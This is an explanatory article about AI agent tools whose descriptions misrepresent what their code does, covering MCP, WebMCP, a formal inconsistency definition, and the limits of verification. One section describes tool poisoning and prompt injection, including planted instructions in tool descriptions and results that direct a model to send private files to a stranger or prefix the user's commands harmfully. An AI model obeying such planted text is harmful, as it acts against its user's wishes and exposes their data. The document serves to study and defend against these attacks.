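# Misrepresented tools: when a tool's description does not match what it does for an AI agent

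## How an agent chooses a tool from its description

An AI agent is a program in which a language model takes actions towards a user's goal. The model acts by calling tools, which are functions that fetch information, such as by searching a catalogue, or change something in the world, such as by paying for an order. To choose a tool, the model normally reads each tool's description, not its code, and picks the tool whose description seems to fit the task. The provider (the person, company or website that publishes the tool) writes the description. Some providers may lie in their descriptions, and honest providers may let theirs go out of date or word them ambiguously.

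Suppose a shopper asks her agent to show her what is in her cart. On the shop's page, the agent finds a tool called "finalizeCart", which might display the final contents of the cart or buy them. The agent has little to go on except the words the shop supplied. If it wrongly assumes that the tool only displays the cart, the shopper pays for goods she only wanted to look at. Victor Huang, an engineer at Microsoft, put this example to a group at the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which develops web standards, in *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP* (Huang, 2025). The group was designing a way for web pages to offer tools to agents.

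### The Model Context Protocol

Agents and tools need a common format for exchanging descriptions, calls and results. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard that supplies one. Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, introduced it in 2024 (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*) and later handed its development to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund under the Linux Foundation. The current version of the specification is dated 28 July 2026. Its announcement reports close to half a billion downloads of the main software kits a month (Model Context Protocol, 2026), though downloads give only a rough idea of how many people or tools use the protocol.

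MCP has two main parties. The server is the program that offers tools, and it may run on the provider's machines or on the user's own. The host is the application that runs the model, forwards its tool calls and may ask the user to approve them. (MCP's documents often speak of the "client", the part of the host that exchanges messages with a server.)

The server sends a short block of structured text for each tool. The sample below is from *Tools* (2026), part of the Model Context Protocol specification, with the icon removed and labels added after the double slashes.

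```
{
  "name": "get_weather",                     // identifier used in calls
  "title": "Weather Information Provider",   // label for people to read
  "description":                             // explanatory text
    "Get current weather information for a location",
  "inputSchema": {                           // the arguments it accepts
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "location": {
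        "type": "string",
        "description": "City name or zip code"
      }
    },
    "required": ["location"]                 // arguments it must have
  }
}
```

A tool's description is everything the model receives about the tool before calling it: the name, the explanatory text and the input schema. (MCP uses "description" for the explanatory text alone.) A provider may also attach annotations, which are structured labels such as one that marks a tool as read-only.

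This sample definition contains no code or information about what happens to the city name once the server has it. The provider could discard each query after looking up the weather or keep it for years, and the definition could be identical in both cases.

### One call, step by step

A call starts when the host sends the server a `tools/list` request for its available tools. The server returns the tools' definitions. The provider wrote these definitions and can see the code behind them, but a host connected over a network receives only the text. If the user has installed the server on her own computer, the code is available to read there, but the protocol does not send it with the definitions.

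Under the specification, a server may add or change tools over time and may show different tools to callers with different permissions, but it must not vary the list from one connection to the next. Servers can notify hosts of changes. The response to `tools/list` also includes a suggested time, five minutes in the specification's sample, during which the host can reuse its copy, so a model may read a definition that the provider replaced a few minutes ago.

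Next the host puts the tool definitions into the model's context, the text the model works from when it produces its next output. The context also contains the user's request, so the model works from the provider's words as well as the user's. Huang's slides list one way a provider can abuse this, known as tool poisoning, which is to plant instructions to the model in a tool's name or explanatory text. Tool names can also clash, since a host that draws on several servers may find two tools named `search`. Model Context Protocol's maintainers recommend that the host tell them apart, for example with a prefix, and warn against relying on the name a server gives itself, because two servers can use the same one.

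The model now picks a tool and fills in the arguments. For the weather tool, it writes the name `get_weather` and the location "New York". To decide whether to call `finalizeCart`, it can use the shopper's request, the shop's description, and whatever it learned in training about how shops use the word "finalize". The model chooses by interpreting text, and nothing at this stage checks its interpretation against the tool's code.

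The input schema also affects what information the agent discloses, so the arguments an agent supplies can do harm even when it has picked the right tool. Huang contrasted a dress-search tool that takes size and price as inputs with one that also takes age, pregnancy status and location. An agent that knows these things about the shopper may fill them in, and the shop could then build a profile of her without her consent.

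The host may ask the user to approve a call before forwarding it. Under the specification, there "should" always be a human who can refuse a call, and hosts "should" show the arguments before sending them. In standards documents, "should" marks strong advice rather than a requirement, so a host that doesn't ask can still conform. A user who is asked is in much the same position as the model. She sees a name or title that the provider wrote and arguments that the model wrote, but not the code. Unless she knows the shop, "Allow finalizeCart?" is hardly clearer to her than the tool's name was to the agent.

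Some hosts may use a second model to check a planned call before it runs. Chrome for Developers (2026), Google's documentation for developers who build for its browser, suggests a "critic" that compares the user's request with the function name and arguments in the call. This can stop an agent that has strayed from the task, for instance because text on a web page misled it. It is much less useful against a tool whose name fits the request but whose code does something else, because the critic relies on the same name.

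If nobody objects, the host sends `tools/call` with the tool's name and arguments. This runs the implementation, which consists of the provider's code and any remote services that code uses. If the server is remote, nobody on the user's side can watch this happen. The specification's security section requires servers to validate inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitize outputs. A server could meet all four requirements and still do something that doesn't match its description.

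The July 2026 version also lets a server request more input in the middle of a call, such as a confirmation. The host then repeats the call with the answer attached. Inian Parameshwaran, head of product at the database company Supabase, welcomed this in the release announcement because Supabase's tools will be able to check with the user before creating a project that costs money or running a query that would delete data. A careful shop could likewise have "finalizeCart" show the total and require confirmation before completing the purchase. But the provider decides whether to ask and how to word the question, and a shop that wanted to hide a purchase from its customer would leave the question out.

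Finally, the server returns a result, which the host passes to the model. If the provider has declared an output schema, the server must return data in that shape and the host should check that it has. This check can confirm that a temperature is a number, but not that the number is correct. The result is also the provider's account of what the tool did. If "finalizeCart" returns "Cart finalized", the agent still doesn't know whether the call charged the shopper.

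### WebMCP, where the web page is the provider

A shop could offer "finalizeCart" through an ordinary MCP server, but Huang's slides concerned WebMCP, a newer, proposed browser interface through which a web page offers tools to an agent. The draft specification, *WebMCP* (Web Machine Learning Community Group), compares such a page to an MCP server whose tools run as script in the page instead of on a remote machine. The page registers a JavaScript function with a name and a description. Brosset (2026) explains in *WebMCP updates, clarifications, and next steps* that the browser translates the page's tools into MCP's format for the agent.

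The steps of a call stay the same, but the code is in the browser, which has to run the page's function. The agent still gets only the metadata before the call and the return value afterwards. The *security privacy questionnaire* that the WebMCP group prepared for its reviewers describes both as limited to what the tool's author declares.

Under the draft, the browser refuses to register a tool if its name is already in use, is too long or contains forbidden characters, if its name or description is empty, or if the browser cannot convert its input schema to text. No step compares the description with the function that the page supplies in the same call.

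Chrome for Developers (2026) argues that WebMCP improves on how agents otherwise use a page. Without it, an agent has to work out what each button and field is for, often over many steps, any of which it can get wrong, whereas WebMCP lets the site declare the purpose. This should be an improvement if the declaration is honest and carefully worded, but an agent that relies on a declared tool may stop looking at the button, the price beside it and the other clues that a human shopper would use. Chrome for Developers also argues that tools run visibly in the page, so users can see that a task has gone as expected. That helps a shopper who is watching, although she may see the purchase only after it has gone through.

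The W3C group developing WebMCP is working on its own version of mid-call questions. At a May 2026 meeting, Brandon Walderman described a tool that orders a product and shows the user a checkout form halfway through, according to W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2026). The agent would see an ordinary tool call and the final result, and need not know about the form. In June the group agreed to specify an "interactive" mode first and left two other modes for later discussion, according to that month's minutes, also titled *WebML CG Teleconference* (2026).

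All of this may still change. Google's page, last updated on 7 October 2026, describes WebMCP as a proposed standard under active discussion. Chrome offers it from version 149 in an origin trial, a public test that websites can join. The specification is a Draft Community Group Report, which is not a W3C standard. MCP Playground, a vendor's blog, dates the current text to 26 August 2026. W3C (2026) minutes show that in June the group was moving the work to a Working Group, a W3C body that can produce formal standards.

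### How the WebMCP group named the problem

The WebMCP group began discussing mismatched tools well before Chrome opened its trial. On 4 November 2025 its chair, Kostiainen (2025), invited members of W3C's security interest group to a session the following week on WebMCP's security and privacy. Less than three hours later Jones (2025) replied in the thread, quoting the WebMCP group's document: "There is no guarantee that the WebMCP tool's declared intent matches its actual behavior."

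Jones thought this was the central issue. He wrote that generative AI makes things up, so a separate layer has to test the intent against the results; otherwise an agent might order goods on his credit card and leave him with the bill. His complaint conflates two failures. A model that makes things up can misuse a tool even when its description is accurate. The sentence he quoted is about tools with wrong descriptions, which would mislead even a model that never made anything up.

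Huang's slides, dated 10 November, use "finalizeCart" as an example under the heading "Misrepresentation of intent". He called the result a three-party ambiguity, since the user, the agent and the site can each understand the call differently, and he left open which of them should be responsible for it. A footnote adds that this is "not really" a security concern. That is fair if security means defence against an attacker, because a shop could have chosen the name in good faith. The sentence in the group's document is broader and covers both careless and dishonest shops, since the shopper is charged in either case.

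By 11 December the group had merged Huang's security document into its repository. Huang estimated in W3C's *WebML CG Teleconference* (2025) that the group was 70 to 80 per cent done identifying the threats. The document stayed separate from the specification for some months, which caused confusion. In February 2026 Jones complained on a W3C mailing list that the security section of WebMCP's explainer, its introductory document, was two sentences long. Hofmann (2026), who works on WebMCP's security at Google, replied that the separate document covered the most relevant risks well. Di Maio argued that no commercial product could deliver "WebMCP security compliance" while the specification did not yet define compliance.

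In May, Hofmann proposed moving Huang's text into the specification as a starting point for a security review and a formal threat model, which nobody had yet drafted. By 25 June, the specification had a security and privacy section (W3C, 2026), and the group had resolved to seek review from W3C's technical architecture, privacy and security groups. In the questionnaire it prepared for them, the group acknowledges that the specification has no binding guidance against the misuse of tools that expose sensitive operations such as purchases. The group intends to add a hint that tool developers can use to flag consequential actions. A shop could then flag "finalizeCart", but the browser would again rely on the shop to label its tool accurately.

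## What counts as misrepresenting a tool

The sentence Jones quoted contrasts a tool's "declared intent" with its "actual behavior", but doesn't specify how much they must differ for the tool to count as misrepresented. When a shop's checkout tool takes an order, it may charge the shopper's card, update the stock count, email a receipt and write a line in a log. Few shoppers would feel misled if the tool's description left out the log, but most would if it left out the charge.

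*Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) formally defines the problem. The group, at Fudan University in China, compared descriptions with code in thousands of MCP tools and found inconsistencies in about a tenth of them.

### The formal definition

Shi and colleagues model a tool as a pair, T = (D, C). D is the description, and C is the code that runs when an agent calls the tool. They define description-code inconsistency (DCI) as follows:

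```
DCI(T) := (Φ_claim ≠ Φ_act) ∨ (Ψ_act ⊈ Ψ_claim)
```

Φ (phi) stands for functionality, the task the tool performs for its caller. Φ_claim is what the provider states or implies in the description, and Φ_act is what the code delivers. Ψ (psi) stands for effects on the environment, such as writing a file, sending data somewhere or using a lot of computing time. Ψ_claim is the set of effects the provider discloses, and Ψ_act is the set that occurs when the code runs. ∨ means "or", and ⊈ means "is not contained in". So a tool is inconsistent if it performs a different task from the one claimed or has at least one effect the provider didn't disclose.

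The paper's running example is a tool with the description "Search local files by name". Φ_claim is a search of local files by name, and Ψ_claim is empty because the provider mentions no effects. If the code searches the files and returns the matches, the tool is consistent. If the code also uploads each query to a remote server, the functionality matches, but the tool is inconsistent because Ψ_act contains an upload that Ψ_claim lacks.

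The formula defines a mismatch, which is any difference between a tool's description and its implementation, whatever the cause. A provider who lies and a provider who changes the code but forgets to update the description can produce the same mismatch. Misrepresentation is narrower, since it requires a mismatch that could mislead an agent or user who is making a decision. Fraud is narrower still, because the provider must know that the claim is false, or not care whether it is true, and intend others to rely on it.

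### Why the effects condition runs one way

Under the formula, claimed and actual functionality must match, but actual effects need only stay within the disclosed ones. This makes sense if disclosed effects work as warnings. A user loses very little if the provider warns that the file search may write an index to the disk and it sometimes doesn't, but if the tool fills her disk without warning, she had no chance to refuse.

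Effects also vary between calls. A search tool might build its index on the first call and reuse it afterwards, so an honest provider has to disclose an effect that most calls won't have. If the formula required the disclosed and actual effects to be equal, this tool would be inconsistent every time it reused its index.

A one-way condition is weak because a provider can meet it by disclosing every possible effect. A description that includes the warning "may read, change, delete or transmit any data" covers anything the tool could do to the user's data. But an agent would learn almost nothing from the warning, and a user who saw it on every tool would soon stop reading it. The formula does not penalize such warnings.

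### The seven subtypes

Shi and colleagues divide inconsistencies into four kinds of mismatched functionality and three kinds of undeclared side effect. All seven appear below as variations on the file search.

| Subtype | Description | What the code does | Condition |
|---|---|---|---|
| Undeclared functionality | "Search local files by name" | Searches local files and cloud storage | Φ_claim ⊂ Φ_act |
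| Overclaimed functionality | "Search local and cloud files by name" | Searches local files only | Φ_act ⊂ Φ_claim |
| Misclaimed functionality | "Search local files by name" | Deletes the local file with that name | Φ_claim ∩ Φ_act = ∅ |
| Ambiguous functionality | "Process local files" | Searches local files by name | ¬∃! Φ_claim |
| Resource overconsumption | "Search local files by name" | Indexes the whole disk, then searches | An undisclosed effect uses resources at a cost above a threshold, τ |
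| State mutation | "Search local files by name" | Gives every account on the computer full access to the folder, then searches it | An undisclosed effect changes something that persists after the call |
| Data leakage | "Search local files by name" | Searches, then uploads the query | An undisclosed effect sends sensitive data to an external destination |

The symbol ⊂ means "is a smaller part of", so in the undeclared case the tool does everything in its description and something more. An agent trying to search only the files on this laptop would unknowingly contact a cloud service and get its results mixed in. In overclaiming, the tool does only part of what its description says. The agent may choose it over another tool with a more modest and accurate description, find nothing, and tell the user that her file doesn't exist.

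A tool has misclaimed functionality when the task in its description and the task it performs don't overlap at all. For example, a user who asks for a file loses it. Functionality is ambiguous when the description doesn't claim exactly one task, a case the report covers separately below.

The three side-effect subtypes are harder for a user to notice because the search still returns the right files. The result may not show that other accounts on her computer can now alter them.

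The categories of functionality and effects overlap. A tool that searches cloud storage must send the file name to the cloud service, so the example of undeclared functionality also involves an undeclared transfer of data. Shi and colleagues accept that the two types can occur together and count each tool under a primary subtype.

The four functionality subtypes also don't cover every functionality mismatch. Suppose a provider says its tool searches local and cloud files, but the code searches local files and email. The description and the code each include something the other lacks, so the tool is clearly inconsistent under the formula, but strictly it doesn't meet the conditions for any of the subtypes. This is a problem for anyone counting subtypes, though it makes little difference to an agent deciding whether to trust the tool.

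### Safeguards that are missing

The one-way condition causes more serious trouble when the missing behavior is a safeguard. One tool in the study places orders on the MAX exchange. According to its description, the user must explicitly approve a confirmation prompt before an order goes through, but the code submits the order immediately.

If the prompt counts only as an effect (a message appears on the user's screen), the tool can omit it, because the effects condition permits a disclosed effect not to occur. To avoid this result, a promised safeguard has to count as part of the claimed functionality. The provider claimed that the tool places orders after the user approves them, but the code places them without the approval step. Shi and colleagues do classify the tool as overclaimed functionality. They also give it a state-mutation label, presumably because an order without approval is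 a change that the provider never disclosed.

*Don’t believe everything you read* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) uses a narrower definition that would miss this tool's fault. Its detector, MCPDiff, extracts one list of features from a server's code and another from the server's documents, such as the README file, and looks for code features that the documents omit. (The model does not necessarily see the README, so this is a slightly different comparison.) The paper treats the reverse case, where a provider claims a feature that the code lacks, as "ignorable under our threat model".

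That rule is reasonable if the missing feature is cloud search and the worry is about concealed functions, since the usual result is a failed task. It is a poor one for safeguards, because people who think a safeguard is in place take risks they would otherwise avoid. A user might let her agent trade unattended only because she expects to see every order before it is placed.

Other software may rely on the safeguard as well. According to W3C minutes from December 2025, the WebMCP group discussed how to avoid prompting the user twice, once from the site and once from the agent. If an agent skips its own prompt because the site has promised one, and the site doesn't show it, the user gets no prompt.

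### Which omissions are material

Under a literal reading of the formula, nearly every tool would count as misrepresented, because no provider lists every effect. Li and colleagues give the example of a tool described as "Query a user's profile information from the database by user ID." The code returns the user's name and email address, but it also updates the record's "last access" time to the present. Under the formula, this update is an undeclared change to persistent state, so the tool gets the same verdict as the one that opens a folder to every account on the computer.

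The same omission can be trivial for one user and important for another. The new timestamp makes no difference to most people who look up a profile. But if a company deletes accounts that nobody has opened for a year, its agent's routine look-ups would keep unused accounts from ever being deleted, and the company would want to know that.

This suggests that an omission is material if the missing fact could reasonably change whether an agent or user calls the tool, what information they give it, or whether the agent asks the user first.

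*From Docs to Descriptions* (2026) models tool selection as a function that takes the user's query and the available tools, and returns either one tool or none. One can then compare the selected tool with the best tool for the query. In these terms, an omission is material if adding the missing fact would change the selection, including to no tool. The missing fact can also affect how someone uses the tool. A user who learns that the file search uploads her queries may still want to use it, but she might avoid typing in the name of her illness.

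Shi and colleagues' formula has no general test of materiality. It counts resource use only above a threshold τ and data leakage only when the data is "sensitive", but it counts any lasting change of state. In practice, they leave much of the judgment to a language model, and their prompts replace τ with the word "excessive". Their detector prompts the model twice about each tool, once to look for consistency and once to look for inconsistency. If the answers differ, a further prompt asks the model to decide whether the alleged problem is "a significant violation or a trivial nitpick".

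The detector also stops following a tool's code when it reaches a library listed as benign, and the list includes logging libraries. This is sensible for most logs, which help programmers find faults, but a log can contain a medical query or a card number, and a company other than the provider may store it. A fixed list of harmless operations can save a lot of work, but it isn't enough to determine what is material.

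Li and colleagues grade servers by how closely their documents match their code, as a percentage, rather than giving a yes-or-no verdict. They put servers that score between 80 and 100 per cent in a "mostly match" group, whose deviations they regard as minor and acceptable. A server with twenty features would score 95 per cent if its documents omitted only the one that trades with real money. A proportion like this measures how complete the documentation is, and it can be very high even when the documents omit what a user most needs to know.

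A provider writes one description for everybody and can't be expected to know about the company with the dormant accounts. A fair standard is probably what a typical user of that kind of tool would want to know, plus anything the provider has learned that a particular user depends on. This is compatible with Shi and colleagues' advice that developers disclose auxiliary functions, external data flows, changes of state and "unusually high resource costs". The word "unusually" helps, since an email tool doesn't need a warning that it sends messages over the internet, though people will still disagree about what is usual.

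### Ambiguous descriptions

The formula requires a single claimed functionality to compare with the code. "Process local files" and "finalizeCart" don't specify one. The first, for example, could mean searching, renaming, compressing or deleting files. For these tools, there is no definite answer to whether Φ_claim equals Φ_act.

Shi and colleagues count ambiguity in a description as an inconsistency. That judgment depends only on the text, since "Process local files" is equally vague whatever the code does. This is fine as a rule for writing descriptions, but less helpful for judging how badly a particular tool could mislead someone.

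A better approach is to list the reasonable readings of the description and compare the code with each. If "finalizeCart" only displays the cart, an agent that reads it as a purchase may leave the shopper waiting for a present that never arrives. If it completes the purchase, an agent that reads it as a display spends her money without her consent. The name is equally ambiguous in both cases, but the likely harm is greater when the tool makes the purchase. An ambiguous description is a misrepresentation when at least one reasonable reading is false and acting on that reading could matter to the user.

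Whether a reading is reasonable may depend on the reader. Huang asked whether sites should have to test their tool names with different browser agents and in different languages. A reading that few English-speaking shoppers would consider might be common for a particular model or natural in translation.

### Tool poisoning and prompt injection

Misrepresentation overlaps with two better-known problems, prompt injection and tool poisoning. Prompt injection means getting a model to follow instructions that an attacker has placed in the text it reads. Tool poisoning is prompt injection in which the instructions are in a tool's description. According to Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification*, these instructions are visible to the model but not to the user.

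A tool can have a false description, planted instructions, both, or neither. The table shows these four combinations for the file search.

| | No planted instructions | Planted instructions |
|---|---|---|
| True description | The tool searches local files, as claimed, and does nothing else of importance. | The tool searches local files, as claimed, but its description also contains an order to the model to send private files to a stranger. |
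| False description | The tool uploads every query, and its description gives no hint of this. | The tool uploads every query without disclosing it, and its description also contains an order to the model to send private files to a stranger. |

The bottom row of the table covers misrepresentation, and the right-hand column covers prompt injection. Shi and colleagues make the same distinction, pointing out that a tool can be inconsistent without an attack, whereas tool poisoning is a deliberate attempt to steer the model.

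The two problems also cause harm at different times. A false claim about a tool can mislead an agent only when the agent considers using that tool, while planted instructions can work as soon as the host loads the description. *Jumping the line*, by the security company Trail of Bits, reports a test in which a tool's description told the agent to add a harmful prefix to the user's commands and gave a false explanation of what the prefix did. The applications tested, including Claude Desktop, followed the instruction while using other tools. The agent never had to call the malicious tool, so requiring the user to approve each call to that tool would not have stopped the attack.

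Planted instructions can also arrive in a tool's results, so some accurately described tools belong in the top right of the table. A tool that fetches customer reviews may do what its provider claims and still return a review in which a stranger has hidden instructions to the agent. Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP Can Be Used To Hijack AI Agents, Chrome Warns* reports Google's warning that even trusted tools can pass on such instructions when they return comments, reviews or forum posts. The WebMCP group has also considered the reverse attack, in which the agent's input to a tool carries instructions to a model run by the site. Hofmann wanted to leave such attacks out of the group's threat model, according to W3C's December minutes.

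Providers can legitimately include instructions in a tool's description, such as when to use the tool or what format a date should take. An instruction is "planted" here if it directs the model to act against the user's wishes or to do something unrelated to using the tool properly. Some wording is harder to classify. "The best file search available" contains no instruction and is too vague to be clearly false, but it might still lead the model to call the tool more often than its quality justifies.

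Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026) list 38 kinds of threat to MCP systems in *MCP-38*, with separate entries for instructions hidden in descriptions, instructions hidden in content that tools fetch, and metadata that biases the model towards a tool. None of the 38 headings is for a description that was false from the start. This may be because they built the list by asking what an adversary could control, inject, forge or exhaust, and a provider who forgets to update a description isn't an adversary. In explaining their method, though, they describe tool description poisoning more loosely, as altering a description to mislead the model, which would include some plain lies about what a tool does.

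### False results and later changes

A tool described as "Pay an invoice" might pay the invoice but then return an error message, so the agent believes the payment failed and pays again. The tool performed the claimed task, and the payment was a disclosed effect. This is an inconsistency under the formula only if the claimed functionality includes accurately reporting what happened.

It seems right to count a tool as misrepresented if it misreports its own results. The agent often has no other way to learn the outcome, as any provider of a payment tool knows. The case is even clearer for tools that fetch information, because the result is all they provide. A weather tool that adds five degrees to every forecast for a seaside resort doesn't do what its description says. But if the tool accurately passes on a forecast that turns out to be wrong, the provider hasn't misrepresented it, because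 the fault lies in the data.

False results can also hide another kind of mismatch. In a second version of Li and colleagues' profile tool, the code deletes the user's record and returns the status "ok". This is misclaimed functionality whatever the tool returns, but the "ok" status makes the agent less likely to notice the problem.

The other difficult case is a description that was true when the user approved it and became false later. The formula doesn't account for time, so one has to apply it to each version of the tool separately. Suppose a user approves the local file search, and a month later the provider changes the code to upload queries but leaves the description alone. That change makes the tool inconsistent. A remote service that the tool relies on might also start keeping the queries without any change to the tool's own code. Shi and colleagues define C as code, so on a strict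 reading their formula would miss this, although the user is just as misled. It is better to treat the remote service as part of the implementation.

The provider might instead change the code and the description together, so that the tool openly searches both local and cloud files. The description then matches the tool's behavior both before and after the change. But if the host doesn't show the user the new description, she still believes the tool searches only local files, because that is what she approved. Her approval no longer covers what the tool does. Shen and colleagues list changes after approval as a separate threat, and also note that MCP gives clients no way to verify that a tool's description or implementation is still the one the user authorized.

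## Why an agent cannot confirm a tool's effects before calling it

To tell whether a provider has misrepresented a tool, an agent would have to compare the tool's description with its implementation, but it usually has only the description. Shi and colleagues call this the "visibility gap". Their example is a weather tool that fetches the forecast but also saves the city in a local history, updates the user's profile and reports the query to an analytics service. An agent that reads only the description can't tell this tool from one that just fetches the forecast.

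The general argument has four premises:

1. Before a call, the model sees a tool's description but not its implementation.
2. Two implementations with different effects can have the same description.
3. A trial call runs the implementation, so it causes the very effects the agent wanted to know about in advance.
4. The provider's code writes the result, so a provider who misdescribed the tool can also misreport what it did.

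If all of these are true, an agent can't work out a tool's effects by reading its description more carefully, and calling the tool to find out is too late and inconclusive.

An agent that cannot confirm a tool's effects may still have good reason to expect the tool to work as described. For example, an agent may reasonably call a well-known shop's checkout tool, just as a person may reasonably press the shop's "Place order" button without seeing the code behind it. Neither has checked what the code does, but the shop's reputation and its fear of legal trouble are often reason enough to trust it for a small purchase.

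### Reading the source code

Some agents can read a tool's code, because the MCP server is on the user's computer or the WebMCP tool is in the user's browser. An agent that can read the weather tool's code could find the line that contacts the analytics service.

Reading a tool's code helps a lot when all the relevant code is on the user's machine. With a remote server, the provider may publish its source code, but the agent has no evidence that the provider is running that version rather than an older or altered one. Local code often depends on remote services too. For example, an agent can see from a weather tool's code that it sends the city's name to an internet address, but not how long the company at that address keeps the query or whether it sells it.

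A tool's effects can also depend on conditions at the time of the call. Developers often put a new feature behind a switch they control from their own server, so the same code might display a shopper's cart in the morning and charge her card in the afternoon. An agent that read the code would find both branches but would not know which one its call would take.

### What Rice's theorem rules out

Even if the agent has all the code, knows that this is the code that will run, and knows that no remote service is involved, there is still a limit on what it can work out. This limit follows from a theorem that the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951. Rice's theorem states that if some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no procedure can determine for every program, correctly and in finite time, whether it behaves that way. The theorem applies to whether a program uploads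 the user's files, but not to whether it contains the word "upload", which is a property of the program's text and easy to check by searching.

Suppose a checker could always determine whether a tool will ever upload a file. For any program P that uploads nothing itself, we could write a tool that runs P and then uploads a file. This tool uploads a file if and only if P finishes, so the checker could determine whether any such P finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do that for every program, so the checker can't exist.

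*Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (Franco and Gershenson, 2026) applies the same construction to agents. Its example agent calls a harmless tool and then, if that tool ever returns, runs a dangerous program. Predicting whether the agent is safe requires predicting whether the harmless tool will return, so the difficulty comes from the tools even when the agent follows only two trivial rules.

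*No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) describes a program that checks each even number above 2 and performs a forbidden action if it finds one that isn't the sum of two primes. According to Goldbach's conjecture, no such number exists, but mathematicians have neither proved nor refuted the conjecture. Nobody knows whether the program is safe, even though anyone can read all of its code.

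Pérez-Acle also shows that it is easier to confirm that a program breaks a rule of the form "never do X" than that it obeys one. Running the program for long enough will reveal any violation. But however long it runs without doing X, it might do X at the next step, and no other kind of finite evidence can clear every safe program. Leaks of secrets are even harder to check. He counts a program as leaking a secret if its published output depends on the secret, and no procedure can confirm every leak or every absence of one, partly because an observer can't distinguish a program that has stopped publishing from one that is slow.

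These results cover all possible programs with unlimited time and memory, but real tools run on finite machines, and a host can stop them after, say, thirty seconds. A time limit makes the question answerable in principle, but Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right must, for some programs, run for nearly as long as the limit. Franco and Gershenson find that predicting an agent's safety under finite limits is PSPACE-complete, meaning it is as hard as any problem a computer can solve with a reasonable amount of memory. No known method solves all such problems quickly.

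Useful checks are still possible because a check doesn't have to be right about every program. *Intent-Driven Computing* (2026) describes the limit as a conflict between three goals: approving no bad programs, approving every good one, and always finishing. A checker that always finishes can meet either of the first two goals, but not both. For example, a checker for file-search tools could approve only those whose code has no means of contacting the network. It would never approve a tool that uploads queries, and many users would accept it even though it would reject some accurately described tools, such as one that goes online only to look for updates.

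Pérez-Acle similarly argues that a gatekeeper doesn't need to judge every program if it has a checkable list that includes everything it must admit and nothing it must refuse. Such lists always omit some safe programs, including some about as short as the rules that define the list. But in his simulations with 2.2 million random programs, the hard cases seldom arose by chance. They are mainly a problem when someone designs a program to defeat the checker, so partial checks should work better against careless providers than against dishonest ones.

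Another option is to limit how providers write tools. *The Two Boundaries* (2026) points out that checking may become decidable if providers must use a restricted programming language, though this limits what their tools can do. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) proposes ways to produce a machine-checkable proof that a skill (a package of text and scripts for an agent) stays within its declared capabilities. An earlier companion paper called this level of assurance "aspirational". Even with such a proof, the user wouldn't know what a permitted remote service does with the data it receives.

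For most tools, Rice's theorem is probably a smaller obstacle than not having the code. Pérez-Acle's gatekeeper has the complete code and unlimited time, but an agent that calls a remote shop doesn't have the shop's code.

### Trial calls and previews

An agent that can't read a tool's code could test it on something worthless. Before using a file-search tool, for example, it could create a folder of dummy files and search that. Such a test is a good way to catch accidental faults, since a tool that deletes files by mistake will probably delete the dummies too.

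A trial call works only if the agent controls the inputs that determine the harm. If the shop already has the shopper's card on file, "finalizeCart" may not take a card number as input, and a trial call could buy everything in the cart. If the shopper first replaces her card with an invalid one, the shop's code will handle a declined payment, and she'll learn little about what happens when a payment succeeds.

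The provider could instead offer a preview mode, often called a dry run, in which the tool reports what it would do without doing it. A preview of "finalizeCart" might return "This would charge $84.50 to your card." That would clarify the ambiguous name and prevent many accidental purchases. It would also give the shopper a specific claim to check against her bank statement.

A preview can't confirm what a tool will do, because the provider writes the preview too. A preview is often just an extra argument that makes the tool run a different branch of its code, and that branch may not match the one that runs in a real call. A dishonest shop could preview a charge of $84.50 and then charge $845, and an honest shop could cause a mismatch by fixing a pricing error in only one branch. A preview can also have effects of its own, because the agent sends the same inputs to the same server. If a shopper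 is worried that a dress shop will record that she is pregnant, a preview that includes this fact has already disclosed it.

### What a clean record is worth

Suppose an agent has called a tool 300 times without any harm. How much does it know about call 301?

If every call has the same probability p of doing harm, independently of the others, the chance of n harmless calls in a row is (1 − p)^n. To get an upper bound on p, find the value at which such a clean record would have only a 5 per cent chance of occurring:

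```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n
```

The approximation, which statisticians call the rule of three, works because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is very close to −3. After 300 harmless calls, the upper bound on the rate of harm is about 3/300, or 1 per cent, at 95 per cent confidence.

| Harmless calls in a row | Upper bound on the rate of harm (95% confidence) |
|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
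| 30 | 9.5% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

The true rate may be much lower than the bound, or zero. Someone who initially considered every rate from 0 to 100 per cent equally likely would now put the chance of harm on call 301 at 1 in 302, or about 0.3 per cent. But the bound still matters for an agent that keeps using the tool, because if the rate is 1 per cent, the chance of at least one harmful call in the next 300 is about 95 per cent.

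All of this assumes that the tool's behavior doesn't depend on who calls it, when, or what is at stake. A provider can easily break that assumption. Suppose a shop's code charges the right amount for orders under $1,000 and adds a hidden fee to larger ones. After 300 grocery orders under $1,000, the agent has paid exactly what an honest shop would have charged, so those orders are no evidence about whether the fee will apply to a $5,000 order. If the shopper initially thought there was a 2 per cent chance that the shop had such a rule, she should still think so.

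The code could also depend on the date, the customer's country or the number of previous calls. A provider who planned to cheat only once would want to build up a good record first. The same pattern can arise by accident, for example if a bug appears only when a cart contains more than a hundred items.

The record may also overstate how many calls were harmless, because the agent counts a call as harmless if it notices no harm. If a file-search tool uploads every query, all 300 searches may return the right files even though none of them was harmless.

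Random audits can help when a tool's behavior depends on the stakes. If an auditor checks a random sample of real calls, including large orders, and the provider can't predict which calls will be picked, the bound applies to the mix of calls in that sample. But the auditor can find harm only after it has happened, and must detect it without relying on the tool's own report.

### Experiments on trust in tool results

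An agent might still detect a misrepresented tool if the tool returns something that doesn't make sense. Researchers have tested whether models notice false tool results, but most of these experiments use false information, such as a wrong name or number, rather than false reports of a tool's effects. False reports of effects may be even harder to spot, because a model often has some independent knowledge of the facts in a search result but none about whether a shop has just charged a card.

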